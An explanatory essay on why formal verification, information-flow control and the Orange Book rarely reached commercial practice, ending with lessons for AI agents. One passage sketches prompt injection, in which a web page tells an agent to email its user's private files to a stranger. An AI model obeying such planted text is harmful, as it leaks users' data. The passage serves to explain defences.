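# Why principled security methods rarely reached practice, and what that predicts for AI agents

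## What are principled security methods, and what counts as reaching practice?

Principled security methods are techniques for showing that a computer system cannot fail in some stated way. They became a research subject around 1970, when the US armed forces wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer and found no system on the market that could keep users from data they weren't cleared to see. Over the next decades, computer scientists developed mathematical proofs about programs, programming languages that track where secrets go, and small protected components that check every access to data. Most of this work stayed in research, but some of it, mainly tools that search code for faults and languages that prevent certain memory errors, became part of ordinary programming. Researchers now propose the same methods for AI agents, systems in which a language model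 chooses actions and carries them out through software tools, so the record of which methods spread may help predict which ones will be adopted for agents.

### Finding faults and ruling them out

The usual way to secure a program is to look for faults and repair the ones found. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), the report of a panel convened by the US Air Force, criticized this approach by examining "tiger teams", groups of experts who test a system by trying to break into it. Every team the panel knew of had broken in, but closing the holes a team used does not assure the owner that no others remain. If a team did fail, the owner would learn only that the system's security was unknown.

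A password check shows the difficulty on a small scale:

```
stored = read_password_file(user)
guess  = read_keyboard()
if guess == stored:
    print("accept")
else:
    print("reject")
```

Suppose the comparison in the third line looks only at the first eight characters. A user whose password is "tulipgarden" can then log in with "tulipgarage". A tester who tries the right password and a few dozen wrong ones will probably miss the fault, because wrong guesses rarely share the right password's first eight characters. Trying every possible password is hopeless, since there are about 209 billion strings of eight lower-case letters, and this fault shows only in longer ones. The US Department of Defense (1985) likewise wrote in its *Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria* that no test procedure for something as complex as a whole computer can be exhaustive, so a later break-in always remains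 possible.

Ruling the fault out requires a different kind of argument, one that starts from a specification, which is a precise statement of what a system must do or must never do. Here it could be "the program prints 'accept' if and only if the guess and the stored password are the same string". Formal verification means proving mathematically that a program or design meets its specification for every input the proof covers. For the password check, the proof is short. The program prints "accept" only when the comparison is true, and the comparison is true only when the two strings have the same length and agree in every character. That last step is false for the eight-character version, so the proof fails at that step, which points to the fault.

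For anything larger, people write the proof in a proof assistant, software such as Lean, Isabelle or Rocq (formerly Coq) that checks every step. It checks more strictly than a mathematician would. Wayne's *Why Don't People Use Formal Methods?* gives the example that a proof assistant accepts a + (b + c) = (a + b) + c only after someone has proved it or declared it as an assumption. In C++ the assumption would be wrong, because adding one to the largest integer has no defined result, and a proof that relied on it would not apply to a program that reached that limit.

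A correct proof can also rest on a poor specification. Wayne contrasts proving that a program never crashes or accepts a wrong password with proving that it also locks the account after three wrong guesses. If the specification leaves out the lock, the proof still holds even though an attacker can keep guessing forever. Adding a lock is easy once someone has thought of it, but other requirements are hard to state precisely. A person can learn from a few pictures what it means to tell parks from birds, yet there is no obvious formula for it. Wayne observes that many of the more recent successes in verifying code came where the requirement was easy to specify, such as that a compiler must never mistranslate a program.

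Static analysers ask less of the programmer. A static analyser looks for faults in code without running it, usually faults of a few fixed kinds, and the programmer supplies no proof. An analyser is sound if it misses no violation of the property it checks, within its stated assumptions. The price of soundness is often false alarms, warnings about something that cannot happen when the program runs. Purdue University's *Non-interference and Non-deducibility*, a set of lecture slides, contains a function that makes a good illustration:

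```
f(x, y):
    if x > 0: return y + y
    else:     return 2 * y
```

Suppose a program branches on a secret x but returns the same number either way. A cautious analyser warns that the result may reveal x, and the warning is false. Better engineering can reduce such cases but not eliminate them, because no algorithm can decide every question of this kind correctly for every program. Any tool must sometimes miss a fault, raise a false alarm or fail to finish. Many toolmakers choose to miss some faults. *Prudent Design Principles for Information Flow Control* (Bastys, Piessens and Sabelfeld, 2018) describes a movement for "soundiness". Its supporters regard full soundness, which means missing no faults, as virtually impossible for practical analysis of whole programs, and they ask toolmakers to explain and limit what their tools miss.

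### The parts that must work

A proof about the password check is of little use if an attacker can open the password file directly. Anderson's panel wanted a single component, the reference monitor, to check every action a program requests against a policy and allow or refuse it. The panel required any implementation to be tamper-proof, impossible to bypass, and small enough to analyse and test completely.

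These requirements disqualified the commercial systems of the day. Anderson applied them to GCOS III, an operating system for Honeywell computers. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but the operating system suspended that check while it did work on the user's behalf, so some accesses escaped the monitor. Counting GCOS III itself as part of the monitor did not help, because it and its supporting software contained between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse completely. Several break-in exercises had already succeeded against it.

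The Department of Defense later used the term trusted computing base for the parts of a system, including hardware, that must work correctly for its security to hold. Everything outside the base can misbehave without breaking that security. For the password check, the base includes the operating system that guards the password file, the processor, and the compiler that turned the source code into machine instructions. Confidence in the base falls as it grows, so verification projects have tended to pick small targets, such as the operating-system kernel seL4.

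### Labels and noninterference

A reference monitor can decide which programs may read a file, but it doesn't control what a program does with the contents afterwards. Smith's *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* gives the example of a tax program that a user downloads and fills with private financial data. The program has good reason to read the data and to send a bill to its vendor over the internet, but access control cannot establish that the bill leaves out the user's income. Information-flow control addresses this gap by labelling data according to how secret or trustworthy it is, then restricting where the data, and anything computed from it, may go.

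Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, gave the idea its mathematical form. Every item of data belongs to a security class. The relation A → B holds when information in class A may flow into class B, and the operation A ⊕ B gives the class of anything computed from data in A and data in B. In the simplest case there are two classes, L for public data and H for secret data:

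```
Allowed:    L → L,  L → H,  H → H
Forbidden:  H → L
Combining:  L ⊕ L = L,  L ⊕ H = H,  H ⊕ H = H
```

A program may store the sum of a and b in c only if the combined class of a and b may flow into the class of c. If either a or b is secret, the sum is therefore secret too. Denning showed that sensible flow rules lead to a lattice, an ordering in which any two classes have a lowest class that both may flow into and a highest class that may flow into both. Much of the argument is that the rules must be consistent. If a program may copy a into b and then b into c, it must also be allowed to copy a straight into c, because banning that would achieve nothing. The lattice can represent categories as well as levels, so a result that draws on medical and financial records may go only to places cleared for both.

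An explicit flow copies or computes data directly from a source into a destination. An implicit flow reveals information through which branch of a program ran. Denning's example is the statement "if a = 0 then b := 0", where b starts with some other value. Anyone who can read b at the end knows whether a was zero, even when the program assigned nothing. Taint tracking, a lighter form of information-flow control, usually follows only explicit flows. Bastys and colleagues consider that often sufficient when the code isn't malicious and only its inputs are suspect, as on a web server facing malicious requests. But an attacker who writes the code can deliberately leak data through its branches.

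Labels can record trustworthiness as well as secrecy, and the rule then keeps untrusted data out of places that need trusted data. For AI agents, this applies to prompt injection, in which an agent follows instructions hidden in material it reads. A line of text on a web page might tell an agent to email its user's private files to a stranger. If the agent does so, untrusted data has caused an action that leaks secret data.

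Denning's rules constrain the steps a program may take. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, stated the goal itself, separately from any mechanism, and named it noninterference. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does has any effect on what the second group can see. Write w for a sequence of commands by all users, and purge(w) for the same sequence with the first group's commands deleted. Noninterference then requires, for every sequence w and every user u in the second group:

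```
what u sees after w  =  what u sees after purge(w)
```

They were partly motivated by the problem of false alarms. They complained that flow analysis flagged many cases that could not occur but that someone still had to examine.

For a single program with a secret input s and a public input p, the property takes a shorter form. Let f(s, p) be everything a public observer sees. Then for all values of s₁, s₂ and p:

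```
f(s₁, p) = f(s₂, p)
```

Noninterference means that changing the secret never changes what the observer sees. *Language-Based Security* (Chong and Guo, 2024) finds essentially this definition in Cohen's 1976 work on "strong dependency". Because the definition compares two runs of the program, watching a single run can never show that the property holds. *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) describes confidentiality more generally as a property of the set of all possible executions, not of any single one.

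The password check violates strict noninterference even when it works correctly. If the guess is "tulip", the observer sees "accept" when the stored password is "tulip" and "reject" when it is "crocus", so the secret has changed the output. As Smith points out, every rejection eliminates one possible password, and no login program can avoid that. The remedy is declassification, a deliberate, permitted release of secret information. In the version that Bastys and colleagues discuss, the programmer writes declassify(guess == stored), which releases one yes-or-no answer. A careless or hostile programmer could write declassify(stored) and release the password itself. Endorsement, a deliberate decision to treat untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose, carries the same kind of risk for integrity. Strict noninterference would forbid logging in, so a usable system needs exceptions, and someone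 has to judge each one.

The definition also depends on what the observer can see. Smith gives a program that appears to do the same amount of work whatever its secret is. On one server, it took twice as long when the secret was zero because of how the processor cached the data. If f leaves out running time, such a program can satisfy the equation and still leak information about its secret to anyone who can time it.

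### A test of adoption

Early expectations for these methods were high. In 1977 Dorothy Denning and Peter Denning, in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, described a procedure for checking flows that they thought simple enough to fit easily into most existing compilers. A quarter of a century later Sabelfeld and Myers could cite three decades of research and relatively little effect on the design of commercial systems. Papers and working prototypes are clearly a poor guide to adoption, and a stricter test has three conditions:

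1. The method runs in a product.
2. People who did not build the method use it.
3. Its use survives the end of research funding.

Researchers can publish good papers on a prototype for years even if it meets none of these conditions. Outside users matter because inventors know how to work around their own tool's awkward spots, while strangers give up. Funding matters because a grant can pay for expert labour that no customer would pay for.

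The test applies to a method in the form people use. Taint tracking in a product counts as adoption of taint tracking, but not of noninterference. A method can pass the test without making anyone safer, so claims about safety need separate evidence.

Jif, a version of Java with information-flow labels, does not count as having reached practice. Smith called it a mature implementation but reported that the field as a whole had had little practical impact. Rust does count. Its compiler, as Wayne notes, proves memory safety outside sections the programmer marks as unsafe. Companies ship products written in Rust by programmers who had no part in its design, and its upkeep does not depend on research grants.

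## What happened when governments asked for verified secure systems?

The US Department of Defense made the first large attempt to get security proofs into commercial products by trying to create demand for them. In the 1970s the government had paid researchers to build secure operating systems, with poor results. *Mathematics, Technology, and Trust* (MacKenzie and Pottinger, 1997), a history of formal verification and the US military, describes two of these projects. SRI International, a research institute in California, began a "Provably Secure Operating System" in 1973 and wrote a 400-page formal specification for it. Seven years later the team suggested that "Provably" might be read as "potentially". A group at the University of California, Los Angeles, set out to verify a kernel for running Unix securely and completed 35 to 40 percent of the verification.

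In the late 1970s Stephen Walker, who handled computer security policy for the Secretary of Defense, changed the department's approach. The department would publish security criteria, computer makers would build security into their ordinary products, and a government center would rate those products. Walker wanted to put the center in a civilian agency, the National Bureau of Standards. Bobby Inman, the director of the National Security Agency (NSA), pounded the desk at the idea and threatened to go to the President. The center opened inside the NSA in 1981.

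### The Orange Book

The Department of Defense issued its criteria in 1983 and revised them in 1985. People called them the Orange Book, after the color of the cover. The counts in this table come from *The Birth and Death of the Orange Book* (Lipner, 2015) and include repeat evaluations of new versions of the same product.

| Class | Main additions | Evaluations, 1984–1998 |
|---|---|---|
| C1 | Users can protect their files from other users | 1 |
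| C2 | Individual logins, an audit record, no leftover data in reused storage | 32 |
| B1 | Labels on data, with rules that users cannot override | 28 |
| B2 | A formal model of the security policy, a search for covert channels | 6 |
| B3 | A trusted computing base small enough to analyze and test | 5 |
| A1 | A formal specification of the design, with proof that it fits the model | 4 |

The center's staff expected vendors to start at C2, move quickly to B1, which they called "training wheels", and then do the "real work" at B2 and above.

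The labels in the B and A classes followed a model that David Bell and Leonard LaPadula had developed for the Air Force. Under its two main rules, a program may not read data above its clearance, and a program reading secret data may not write to a less secret file. The second rule guards against Trojan horses, programs that do something useful while secretly copying data to where a spy can read it. Together the rules let information move only upward, as in Denning's lattice.

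Designers soon needed exceptions. A print program has to read top-secret documents and also send unclassified ones to the printer queue, but the second rule forbids a program that reads top-secret data from writing unclassified data. Designers exempted such programs and called them "trusted subjects", but a verifier then had to show that each one would not misuse its exemption.

To reach A1, a vendor had to formally specify what the trusted computing base did and show, with a verification tool the center had approved, that the specification agreed with the policy model. The vendor needed only an informal argument that the code matched the specification. Early drafts had included a higher class, A2, that required proof of the code itself, but this was impractical with the tools of the time. MacKenzie and Pottinger cite an estimate, based on one completed project, that a trained specialist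 could verify two to six lines of code a day, and that fewer than 200 such specialists existed. At that rate, one specialist would have needed roughly 35 to 100 years to verify a kernel of 50,000 lines.

Robert Boyer and J Moore, who had built one of the leading automated provers, called it a "travesty of mathematical proof" to verify a design while a separate team wrote the code. Peter Neumann of SRI replied that proofs about code are irrelevant if the specification is wrong, and that the quickest benefit comes from finding mistakes in the design. Projects at one contractor, the System Development Corporation, give both sides some support. On its early projects, the programmers finished first and drifted from the design, so the mathematicians derived the formal specification from the code. On a later project, Blacker, the company had its formal methods team also review the design documents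 and the code, and the team caught problems early. Proof of a whole kernel's code came much later, with systems such as seL4.

A1 also required vendors to use formal methods to look for covert channels, which pass information through parts of a system not meant to carry it. MacKenzie and Pottinger give the example of a file lock. Suppose a top-secret program and an uncleared program can both open the same unclassified file. The top-secret program may read the file but not change it, so it obeys both of Bell and LaPadula's rules. But while it is reading, the system blocks the other program from writing. The top-secret program can send a 1 by reading the file and a 0 by leaving it alone, and the uncleared program can read each bit by trying to write at agreed times.

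Closing every such channel would have slowed the computer badly for legitimate users, so the criteria dealt with how fast a channel could leak. The Department of Defense considered more than 100 bits per second too fast for a system to be called secure, and less than 1 bit per second acceptable in most settings. A 2,000-character page, about 16,000 bits, would leak in under three minutes at the higher rate and in nearly four and a half hours at the lower one. An A1 vendor had to justify every channel it left open.

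### Digital's VAX security kernel

Digital Equipment Corporation, a major computer maker, began planning an A1 kernel for its VAX computers in 1981. A feasibility study supported the plan the next year, and a research prototype was running by 1984. Full testing at outside sites started only in late 1989.

The kernel was a virtual machine monitor, a layer of software that makes one computer behave like several. Each virtual machine could run an ordinary operating system, such as Digital's VMS, while the kernel separated secret work from unclassified work. Customers could keep their existing programs, and security would depend on the kernel rather than on the much larger operating systems above it.

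Digital kept the kernel's development machine off the company network and in a locked cage, inside a laboratory that only the kernel group could enter. This made it harder for anyone to plant a backdoor. But the kernel grew to almost 50,000 executable statements, while a demonstration kernel for the Air Force in the 1970s had needed about 1,000 instructions. The formal specification for Digital's kernel would have exceeded 12,000 lines, and the team never finished it. The builders admitted that the formal work and the engineering were never as closely linked as they had wanted. Even so, they believed the kernel could earn an A1 rating, and they described the outside tests as highly successful.

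Digital canceled it in 1990, before general release. Steven Lipner, the manager responsible, who later wrote the Orange Book history, said the reason was that the market was too small. Some of his colleagues thought there were enough potential users.

The product had weaknesses by then. To save time, the team had left out support for Ethernet, the standard way of connecting computers in an office, and potential customers complained. The VAX model it ran on was slow and expensive next to Digital's newest machines. Many customers were also replacing shared computers with individual workstations, so fewer of them had the problem the kernel solved. Digital had plans to address these weaknesses, but Lipner's group could not convince itself that sales would ever repay the cost. The State Department's export controls on B3 and A1 operating systems would probably also have blocked many sales, even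 to close NATO allies.

### Why so few customers paid for proof

Digital's project took eight years to reach outside testing, which left it with old hardware and no Ethernet support. A faster project might have avoided both problems, but Honeywell's Secure Communications Processor (SCOMP) suggests that speed alone would not have been enough. In 1985, well before Digital's kernel was ready, SCOMP became the first system to earn an A1 rating. Honeywell still sold fewer than 30 of the original version and never broke even.

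When Honeywell planned a version for newer hardware, its marketing staff estimated that an A1 rating would attract at most 5 percent more customers than a B3 rating. The Department of Defense required the same security features for both classes, so the estimate roughly measures how much demand the extra proof alone would add. Export controls covered both classes, so they can't explain the small difference. The estimate was one company's guess about one product, but Honeywell acted on it by dropping further formal work and aiming for B3.

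Blacker, which protected the military's Defense Data Network, also reached A1. Development began in 1984 and the rating came in 1991, after five years of evaluation. A system built for one military network could withstand that delay more easily than a commercial product, whose competitors would release several new models in the meantime.

Evaluation results were also hard to predict. IBM expected a C2 rating for its RACF security software, which an early draft of the criteria had listed as an example C2 candidate. RACF received C1 in 1984, apparently because it did not ensure new files were free of data from deleted ones. IBM's engineers thought the extra check would slow the system too much, though a competing product included it and passed. Evaluators and vendors argued over the meaning of the criteria in an online forum that collected more than 2,500 entries. A 1988 entry defined "security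 relevant" as "anything which the evaluation community feels may be relevant to system security". Lipner recalls vendors hiring people to write design documents that satisfied evaluators but did not guide the programmers.

The government's own purchasing perhaps did the most damage. Agencies asked for strong security in their requests for proposals, then waived or weakened the requirement. MacKenzie and Pottinger describe a vicious circle in which proof and evaluation made secure products late and expensive, so buyers chose newer, cheaper ones. The small market then raised the cost of each secure system, which gave the next buyer even more reason to choose something else. Each agency's choice could be sensible on its own, because it was buying the better computer for its money.

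Private companies did not make up the difference. Banks worried more about someone altering an account than about someone reading it, and they had no system of clearances for the labels to enforce. The labels could be awkward even for the military. The Naval Research Laboratory tried them in an email system that handled several levels of secrecy, and Lipner reports that the result was almost unusable. Schaefer, who contributed to the Orange Book, points out in his retrospective *If A1 is the Answer, What was the Question?* that the book's classes were explicitly meant for standalone computers. By the time vendors could meet the higher classes, customers were networking their computers.

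The government eventually lowered its requirements. A 1987 policy, with the slogan "C2 by '92", told agencies that handled national security information to use C2 systems. This worked much better, because most vendors put their standard operating systems through a C2 evaluation and agencies had little else to buy. But C2 required no formal proof, and in 1996 the C2 rating of Microsoft's Windows NT applied only to machines with no network connection and with their floppy drives disabled.

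### The Common Criteria

European governments wrote their own criteria in the meantime, and vendors needed separate evaluations on each side of the Atlantic. In 1999 an international standard, the Common Criteria, replaced the American and European schemes. By the mid-2010s, seventeen countries were conducting evaluations under it, and another nine accepted the results.

The Common Criteria also largely separated security features from assurance, meaning the evidence that the features work. The Orange Book had tied the two together, so a vendor that wanted credit for a proof also had to supply the whole military system of labels, which made the product larger and the proof harder. British critics in particular considered this a serious flaw because it excluded simple devices with very strong assurance. Under the Common Criteria, a vendor could have a small component verified without adding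 functions its customers didn't want.

That freedom also made it easier to avoid difficult requirements. One of the people behind the Orange Book told MacKenzie and Pottinger that buyers would now "pick and choose" and get hurt, whereas an ordinary program manager could understand a rating like B2 without knowing what went into it. *Musings on a Book of Orange* considers it good that buyers can choose requirements to match the threats they face. Although the Common Criteria made proof easier to sell, it gave most buyers no new reason to pay for it. *Musings* also concludes that higher assurance never took off because it went against commercial practice.

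Certificates also meant little in practice. In the late 1990s independent researchers began to publish faults in commercial software, and Lipner reports that evaluated products did no better under attack than others. The member countries eventually decided that detailed examinations of products brought no benefit. Lipner's comparison mostly concerns ordinary commercial products, so it is evidence against the paperwork of evaluation rather than against proof. In *Thirty Years Later*, Karger and Schell (2002) judged Multics, an operating system that had earned a B2 rating, more secure than the systems of the day. Both had reasons to favor the older approach, since Schell had been deputy director of the center that rated products and Karger had helped to build Digital's kernel.

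### What the effort left behind

Lipner finds it hard to see the effort as anything but a failure if the aim was a good supply of high-assurance systems. As of 2014, only one such system was still on sale, a descendant of SCOMP. The lower classes have a better record. C2 features such as individual access controls and audit records are now common, although Lipner leaves open whether vendors would have added them anyway.

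Defenders of the program can also point to the people it trained and the ideas it funded. Security funding helped SRI develop its verification methods, whose key tool was Boyer and Moore's prover. Honeywell used Goguen and Meseguer's noninterference in a real system, LOCK. Two decades after Digital canceled its kernel, Lipner, Jaeger and Zurko (2012) returned to it in *Lessons from VAX/SVS for High-Assurance VM Systems* for guidance on access control, layering, verification and keeping a kernel small. By then virtual machines were in use throughout the industry, but most had not been formally verified.

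But the government's support was not always good for the tools. Once the center endorsed a verification tool, the tool became subject to export controls, and its developers had to convert it to run on Multics just as other users were moving to individual machines. Walker complained that the conversions used up everyone's energy without advancing the technology. By the mid-1990s, safety-critical systems were replacing security as the leading field for formal verification, with Europe playing a much larger part. MacKenzie and Pottinger hoped that the skills developed for military security would be used there.

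## Why did information-flow languages stay in research?

The Orange Book put its labels on files, users and running programs, so an operating system could not track what a trusted subject, such as the print program, did with data in its own memory. Information-flow languages address this by putting the labels in the program's source code, where a compiler can check each line before the program runs. They also seemed easier to adopt than a secure operating system, because a programmer needed only a new compiler and did not have to wait for a government evaluation.

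The best known of these languages is Jif, a version of Java that Andrew Myers introduced in 1999 as JFlow. Five years later, Steve Zdancewic wrote that methods of this kind had not been "widely (or even narrowly!) used". Askarov and Sabelfeld quoted the remark in *Security-Typed Languages for Implementation of Cryptographic Protocols* (2005). To test whether such languages could cope with real systems, they wrote what was then the largest program in any of them.

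### How Jif checks a program

In Java, `int x` declares x as a whole number. Jif adds a label to the type, so `int{Alice:Bob} x` declares a whole number that belongs to Alice and only Alice and Bob may read. If the programmer leaves a label off, the compiler often infers it or uses a default.

Two labels, L for public and H for secret, are enough to show the check. To catch implicit flows as well as explicit ones, the compiler keeps a program-counter label, pc, which records how secret the decisions were that led the program to the current line. In Denning's notation, an assignment of an expression e to a variable x must satisfy:

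```
label(e) ⊕ pc  →  label(x)
```

At the start of the program, pc is L. Inside a branch on a condition c, pc becomes pc ⊕ label(c), and it returns to its earlier value after the branches rejoin.

Suppose h is secret and l is public. The direct copy "l := h" fails because label(h) is H, and H may not flow to L. The next program never copies h, but l ends up holding the same information:

```
if (h) l := 1
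else   l := 0
```

The compiler checks it as follows:

```
before the if:        pc = L
inside each branch:   pc = L ⊕ H = H
"l := 1" requires:    L ⊕ H → L,  that is,  H → L   (forbidden)
```

The assignment in the other branch fails the same way. The constants 1 and 0 are public, so a checker without the program-counter label would have accepted both lines.

The rule also rejects some harmless programs. Add one line to the example:

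```
if (h) l := 1
else   l := 0
l := 0
```

Now l is always 0 at the end, so an observer who sees only the final value learns nothing about h. The compiler still rejects the program, because it checks each assignment against the labels at that point, regardless of what happens to l later. A more elaborate checker could track l to the last line and accept this program, but it would still reject some other harmless program.

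In Jif, the declaration of each method (a named piece of code that other code can call) states how secret a context the method may run in. Code inside a branch on a secret therefore can't call a method that writes to public variables. These declarations let the compiler check a large program one method at a time. It does most of this checking before the program runs, so speed was never the main objection to Jif.

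### False alarms from exceptions

The rule works well on small examples, but ordinary Java code is full of exceptions. When a program divides by zero, or uses a variable that refers to no object, it throws an exception, which means that it abandons what it was doing and jumps to code that handles the error. The jump can reveal a secret just as a branch can. Chong, Vikram and Myers, in *SIF* (2007), describe a version of this problem that often caught new Jif programmers:

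```
x = o.m();
y = 42;
```

If o refers to no object, the first line fails and the second never runs. Anyone who later sees 42 in y therefore learns that o refers to an object. Almost any line of Java can fail like this, so once a secret is involved, the compiler has to treat almost every line as a possible leak.

King, Hicks and colleagues measured the effect in *Implicit Flows* (2008). They chose six security functions from two established libraries, all written in ordinary Java without Jif in mind. Three were ways of logging in to J2SSH, a server for secure remote access, and three were cryptographic functions from Bouncy Castle. The researchers marked the secrets, such as keys and the operating system's password records, and ran JLift, a modified Jif compiler that applies the same checks to a whole Java program without anyone rewriting it. They then examined every alarm by hand and counted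 it as true only if they could confirm that the program could take the reported path.

| Function | Alarms | Explicit flows | Implicit flows | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Password login | 7 | 0 | 7 | 3 |
| Keyboard-interactive login | 23 | 0 | 23 | 19 |
| Public-key login | 170 | 0 | 170 | 111 |
| RSA encryption | 218 | 3 | 215 | 186 |
| MD5 hashing | 209 | 4 | 205 | 199 |
| DES encryption | 260 | 10 | 250 | 207 |
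| Total | 887 | 17 | 870 | 725 |

The tool found 162 true leaks, of which 17 were explicit and 145 implicit. All 725 false alarms came from implicit flows.

Exceptions caused 824 of the 870 implicit alarms, and 706 of those were false. All 706 came from five kinds of unchecked exception, which Java does not force programmers to handle. Null pointer errors, where a variable refers to no object, produced the most, with 455 false alarms out of 475. Array errors, where a program reads past the end of a list, produced another 204 out of 233. In one part of the DES code, nearly every line raised an alarm because the code looks up values in fixed tables and the tool could not determine that the positions were always valid. King and colleagues confirmed by hand that none of those lines could fail. To rule out the alarms, a compiler would have had to establish what the tables contained and that they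 never changed.

Ordinary branches did much better. They caused only 46 alarms, and 14 were false. (The published false alarms for exceptions and branches add up to 720, five short of the total, so the split is slightly uncertain.)

The study did not record how long the examination took, but an assumed ten minutes per alarm gives a rough idea of the cost to a programmer:

| Flows checked | Alarms | Time | True leaks found |
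|---|---|---|---|
| Explicit only | 17 | 2 hours 50 minutes | 17 |
| Explicit and ordinary branches | 63 | 10 hours 30 minutes | 49 |
| All, including exceptions | 887 | 147 hours 50 minutes | 162 |

The full check would take nearly four working weeks for six functions. Each implicit leak would take an hour to find, compared with ten minutes for an explicit one. Few managers would approve that much time for code that already appears to work.

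But the simpler check misses 145 of the 162 leaks, or about 90 percent. It reports nothing on the J2SSH login code, where the full check found 67 true leaks. Login code rarely copies a password. It reveals information through its decisions about what to do next, which the simpler check ignores.

It is less clear how much those missed leaks matter, because King and colleagues did not judge their severity. They described most of the true implicit flows as technical violations of noninterference. In the DES code, for example, the size of the encrypted output depended on the size of the secret input. Some login messages revealed whether a username was valid, but only after the user had given the right password. A programmer who worked through all 887 alarms might have found very little worth fixing. King and colleagues recommended checking explicit flows first, then ordinary branches, and exceptions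 last. By their figures, the first two stages would find 49 leaks in less than a tenth of the time all three would take.

Six functions are a small sample, and security code handles secrets on almost every line, so other software might produce fewer alarms. The study also tested code that wasn't written for Jif, and a programmer who starts in Jif can avoid some alarms by changing style. In the example from Chong and colleagues, the first line can become "if (o != null) { x = o.m(); }", which lets the compiler verify that o is not null when the method is called.

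Programmers can also make such changes just to get their code to compile. In Civitas, a remote voting system with more than 13,000 lines of Jif, King and colleagues found 568 places where the code caught an exception and did nothing about it. The programmers had named the exception "imposs", for impossible, in 429 of them and "unlikely" in another 13. If one of these errors does occur, the program ignores it and carries on. The programmers were probably right about most of them, but the compiler had still required them to write hundreds of handlers for errors they did not expect.

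### What it took to write a real program

Until the mid-2000s almost nobody had used these languages for anything large. Hicks, Ahmadizadeh and McDaniel (2006), in *From languages to systems*, described earlier uses as "toy" programs and presented their email client, JPmail, as the first real-world application in a security-typed language. They had not created Jif, the language they used, so JPmail is better evidence than a demonstration by Jif's designers would have been. To build it, they had to add tools, services and extensions to the language.

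Askarov and Sabelfeld give the best figures for the effort of programming in Jif. Their program let two people play poker over a network without trusting each other or a third party to deal the cards. Each player shuffles the deck secretly, the players exchange encrypted cards, and both reveal their keys at the end to check for cheating. Askarov, then a graduate student, wrote a version in Java in about 60 hours. Converting it to Jif took another 150 hours, and a Jif version that ran as separate programs for the two players took 80 more. The finished program had about 4,500 lines.

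Adding labels to a working program took two and a half times as long as writing it, not counting the time Askarov spent learning Jif. One student's experience with one program can't establish a general ratio, and a second project would presumably have gone faster. The work did uncover some weaknesses in the Java version. Several involved exceptions that could reveal information about secret values, though Askarov and Sabelfeld admitted they saw no obvious way to exploit them.

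The SIF project at Cornell, where Jif was developed, reported better results. SIF is a framework for writing web applications in Jif, and Chong and colleagues used it to build a shared calendar and an email-like system in which some messages need a reviewer's approval. The two applications and a library for managing users came to 4,029 lines, about a quarter of which carried labels. The calendar handled at most 29 percent fewer requests per second than a similar program in ordinary Java, a slowdown that would be tolerable for many websites.

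Only one of the 39 deliberate releases of information or trust in SIF's code was there because the compiler had been too cautious. This is compatible with King and colleagues' less encouraging result, because the two projects measured different things. Chong and colleagues wrote new code to suit the compiler and counted only the exceptions they still needed, while King and colleagues used existing code as it was. Most companies have far more existing code than new code, so King and colleagues' result is closer to their situation.

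### Deciding what to release

The compiler cannot check whether a programmer has chosen the right information to declassify. In *Declassification*, Sabelfeld and Sands considered this problem the key to getting information-flow research into standard practice. They sorted existing proposals by whether each one controlled what information a program releases, who may release it, where in the code or system the release happens, or when it happens.

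Controlling only one of these leaves gaps. Sabelfeld and Sands give the example of a shop that may record up to four digits of a credit card number with each purchase. If the policy doesn't restrict who picks the digits, an attacker can ask for different ones each time and collect all sixteen in four purchases.

Even a precise rule about what a program releases can permit too much. One such rule, delimited release, extends the definition of noninterference. Let e(s, p) be the value that the programmer has chosen to declassify, and let f(s, p) again be everything a public observer sees. Then for all values of s₁, s₂ and p:

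```
if  e(s₁, p) = e(s₂, p)   then   f(s₁, p) = f(s₂, p)
```

The observer may see different outputs for two secrets only if the declassified value, e, also differs between them. For the password check, e is the answer to "does the guess match?", and the rule works as intended because two stored passwords that both differ from the guess must produce the same output.

Now suppose the programmer declassifies an encrypted copy of the secret. With a fixed key, two different secrets always have different encrypted forms, so the condition after "if" is never true for them and the rule no longer restricts the program. Sabelfeld and Sands point out that a program could release the encrypted copy, then print the secret itself, and still satisfy the definition. The definition does not account for encryption being hard to reverse.

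The poker program shows how often such decisions come up. Its main class had 14 declassifications. Eight released signatures, encrypted cards or other data that the protocol needed to send. Another three revealed the players' keys and shuffles, which was safe only once the game had ended. Jif could not express that condition, so Askarov and Sabelfeld had to add a "seal", a flag that changes when the program reveals the keys, so that any later attempt to continue the game causes an error. The program checks the seal as it runs, so the compiler's guarantee does not cover it.

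SIF's applications contained 180 annotations that lowered a label, about one for every 22 lines. Chong and colleagues grouped these into 39 deliberate releases of information, since a single release often needs several annotations. Twelve were inherent in what the applications did, such as showing an event's details to a newly invited guest. Another 26 arose because the builders had used labels to control access to shared data, such as the list of all events.

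This is arguably still progress, because a reviewer of the poker program can concentrate on 14 marked places, whereas in an ordinary program a leak could be anywhere. Some programs need no declassifications. One example is a Jif version of logrotate, a Unix utility that renames and deletes old log files. But programs that talk to users or other computers usually have to release some confidential information, and their programmers still have to make the hardest security decisions.

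### Labels that spread, and libraries without any

Many declassifications exist only because labels spread to results that are safe to publish. In the poker program, each player signs messages with a private key. The signature depends on the key, so the compiler labeled the signature secret, and the program had to declassify it before sending the message. Without such exceptions, the secret label spreads to more and more of a program's data until the program can no longer send anything useful.

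Information-flow labels affect the design of a program as well as its data. Chong and colleagues sometimes had to change a method's declaration several times, first when they found unexpected flows while writing the method, and again when they called it from a new place. Programmers normally divide code into methods so that they can change the inside of one without touching the rest. Labels weaken that separation because a new use of a secret inside a method may require changes to its declaration, and then to the methods that call it.

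Relabeling lists and other data structures takes more work. Suppose a program could relabel a public list of cards as Alice's secret hand without copying it. The old public name would still refer to the same list, so a secret card added under the new name would be visible under the old one. Jif prevents this by making the programmer copy the structure piece by piece. Askarov and Sabelfeld wrote a separate class to hold these copying routines.

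Existing libraries had no labels. A modern program relies on library code for tasks such as networking, storage and encryption, and nobody was going to rewrite all of Java's libraries in Jif. Jif programmers instead wrote signatures, which are files that describe the flows in a library method. The compiler checks the program against the signature and assumes the signature is correct. SIF needed 960 lines of signatures, nearly a quarter of the length of its applications and user library combined.

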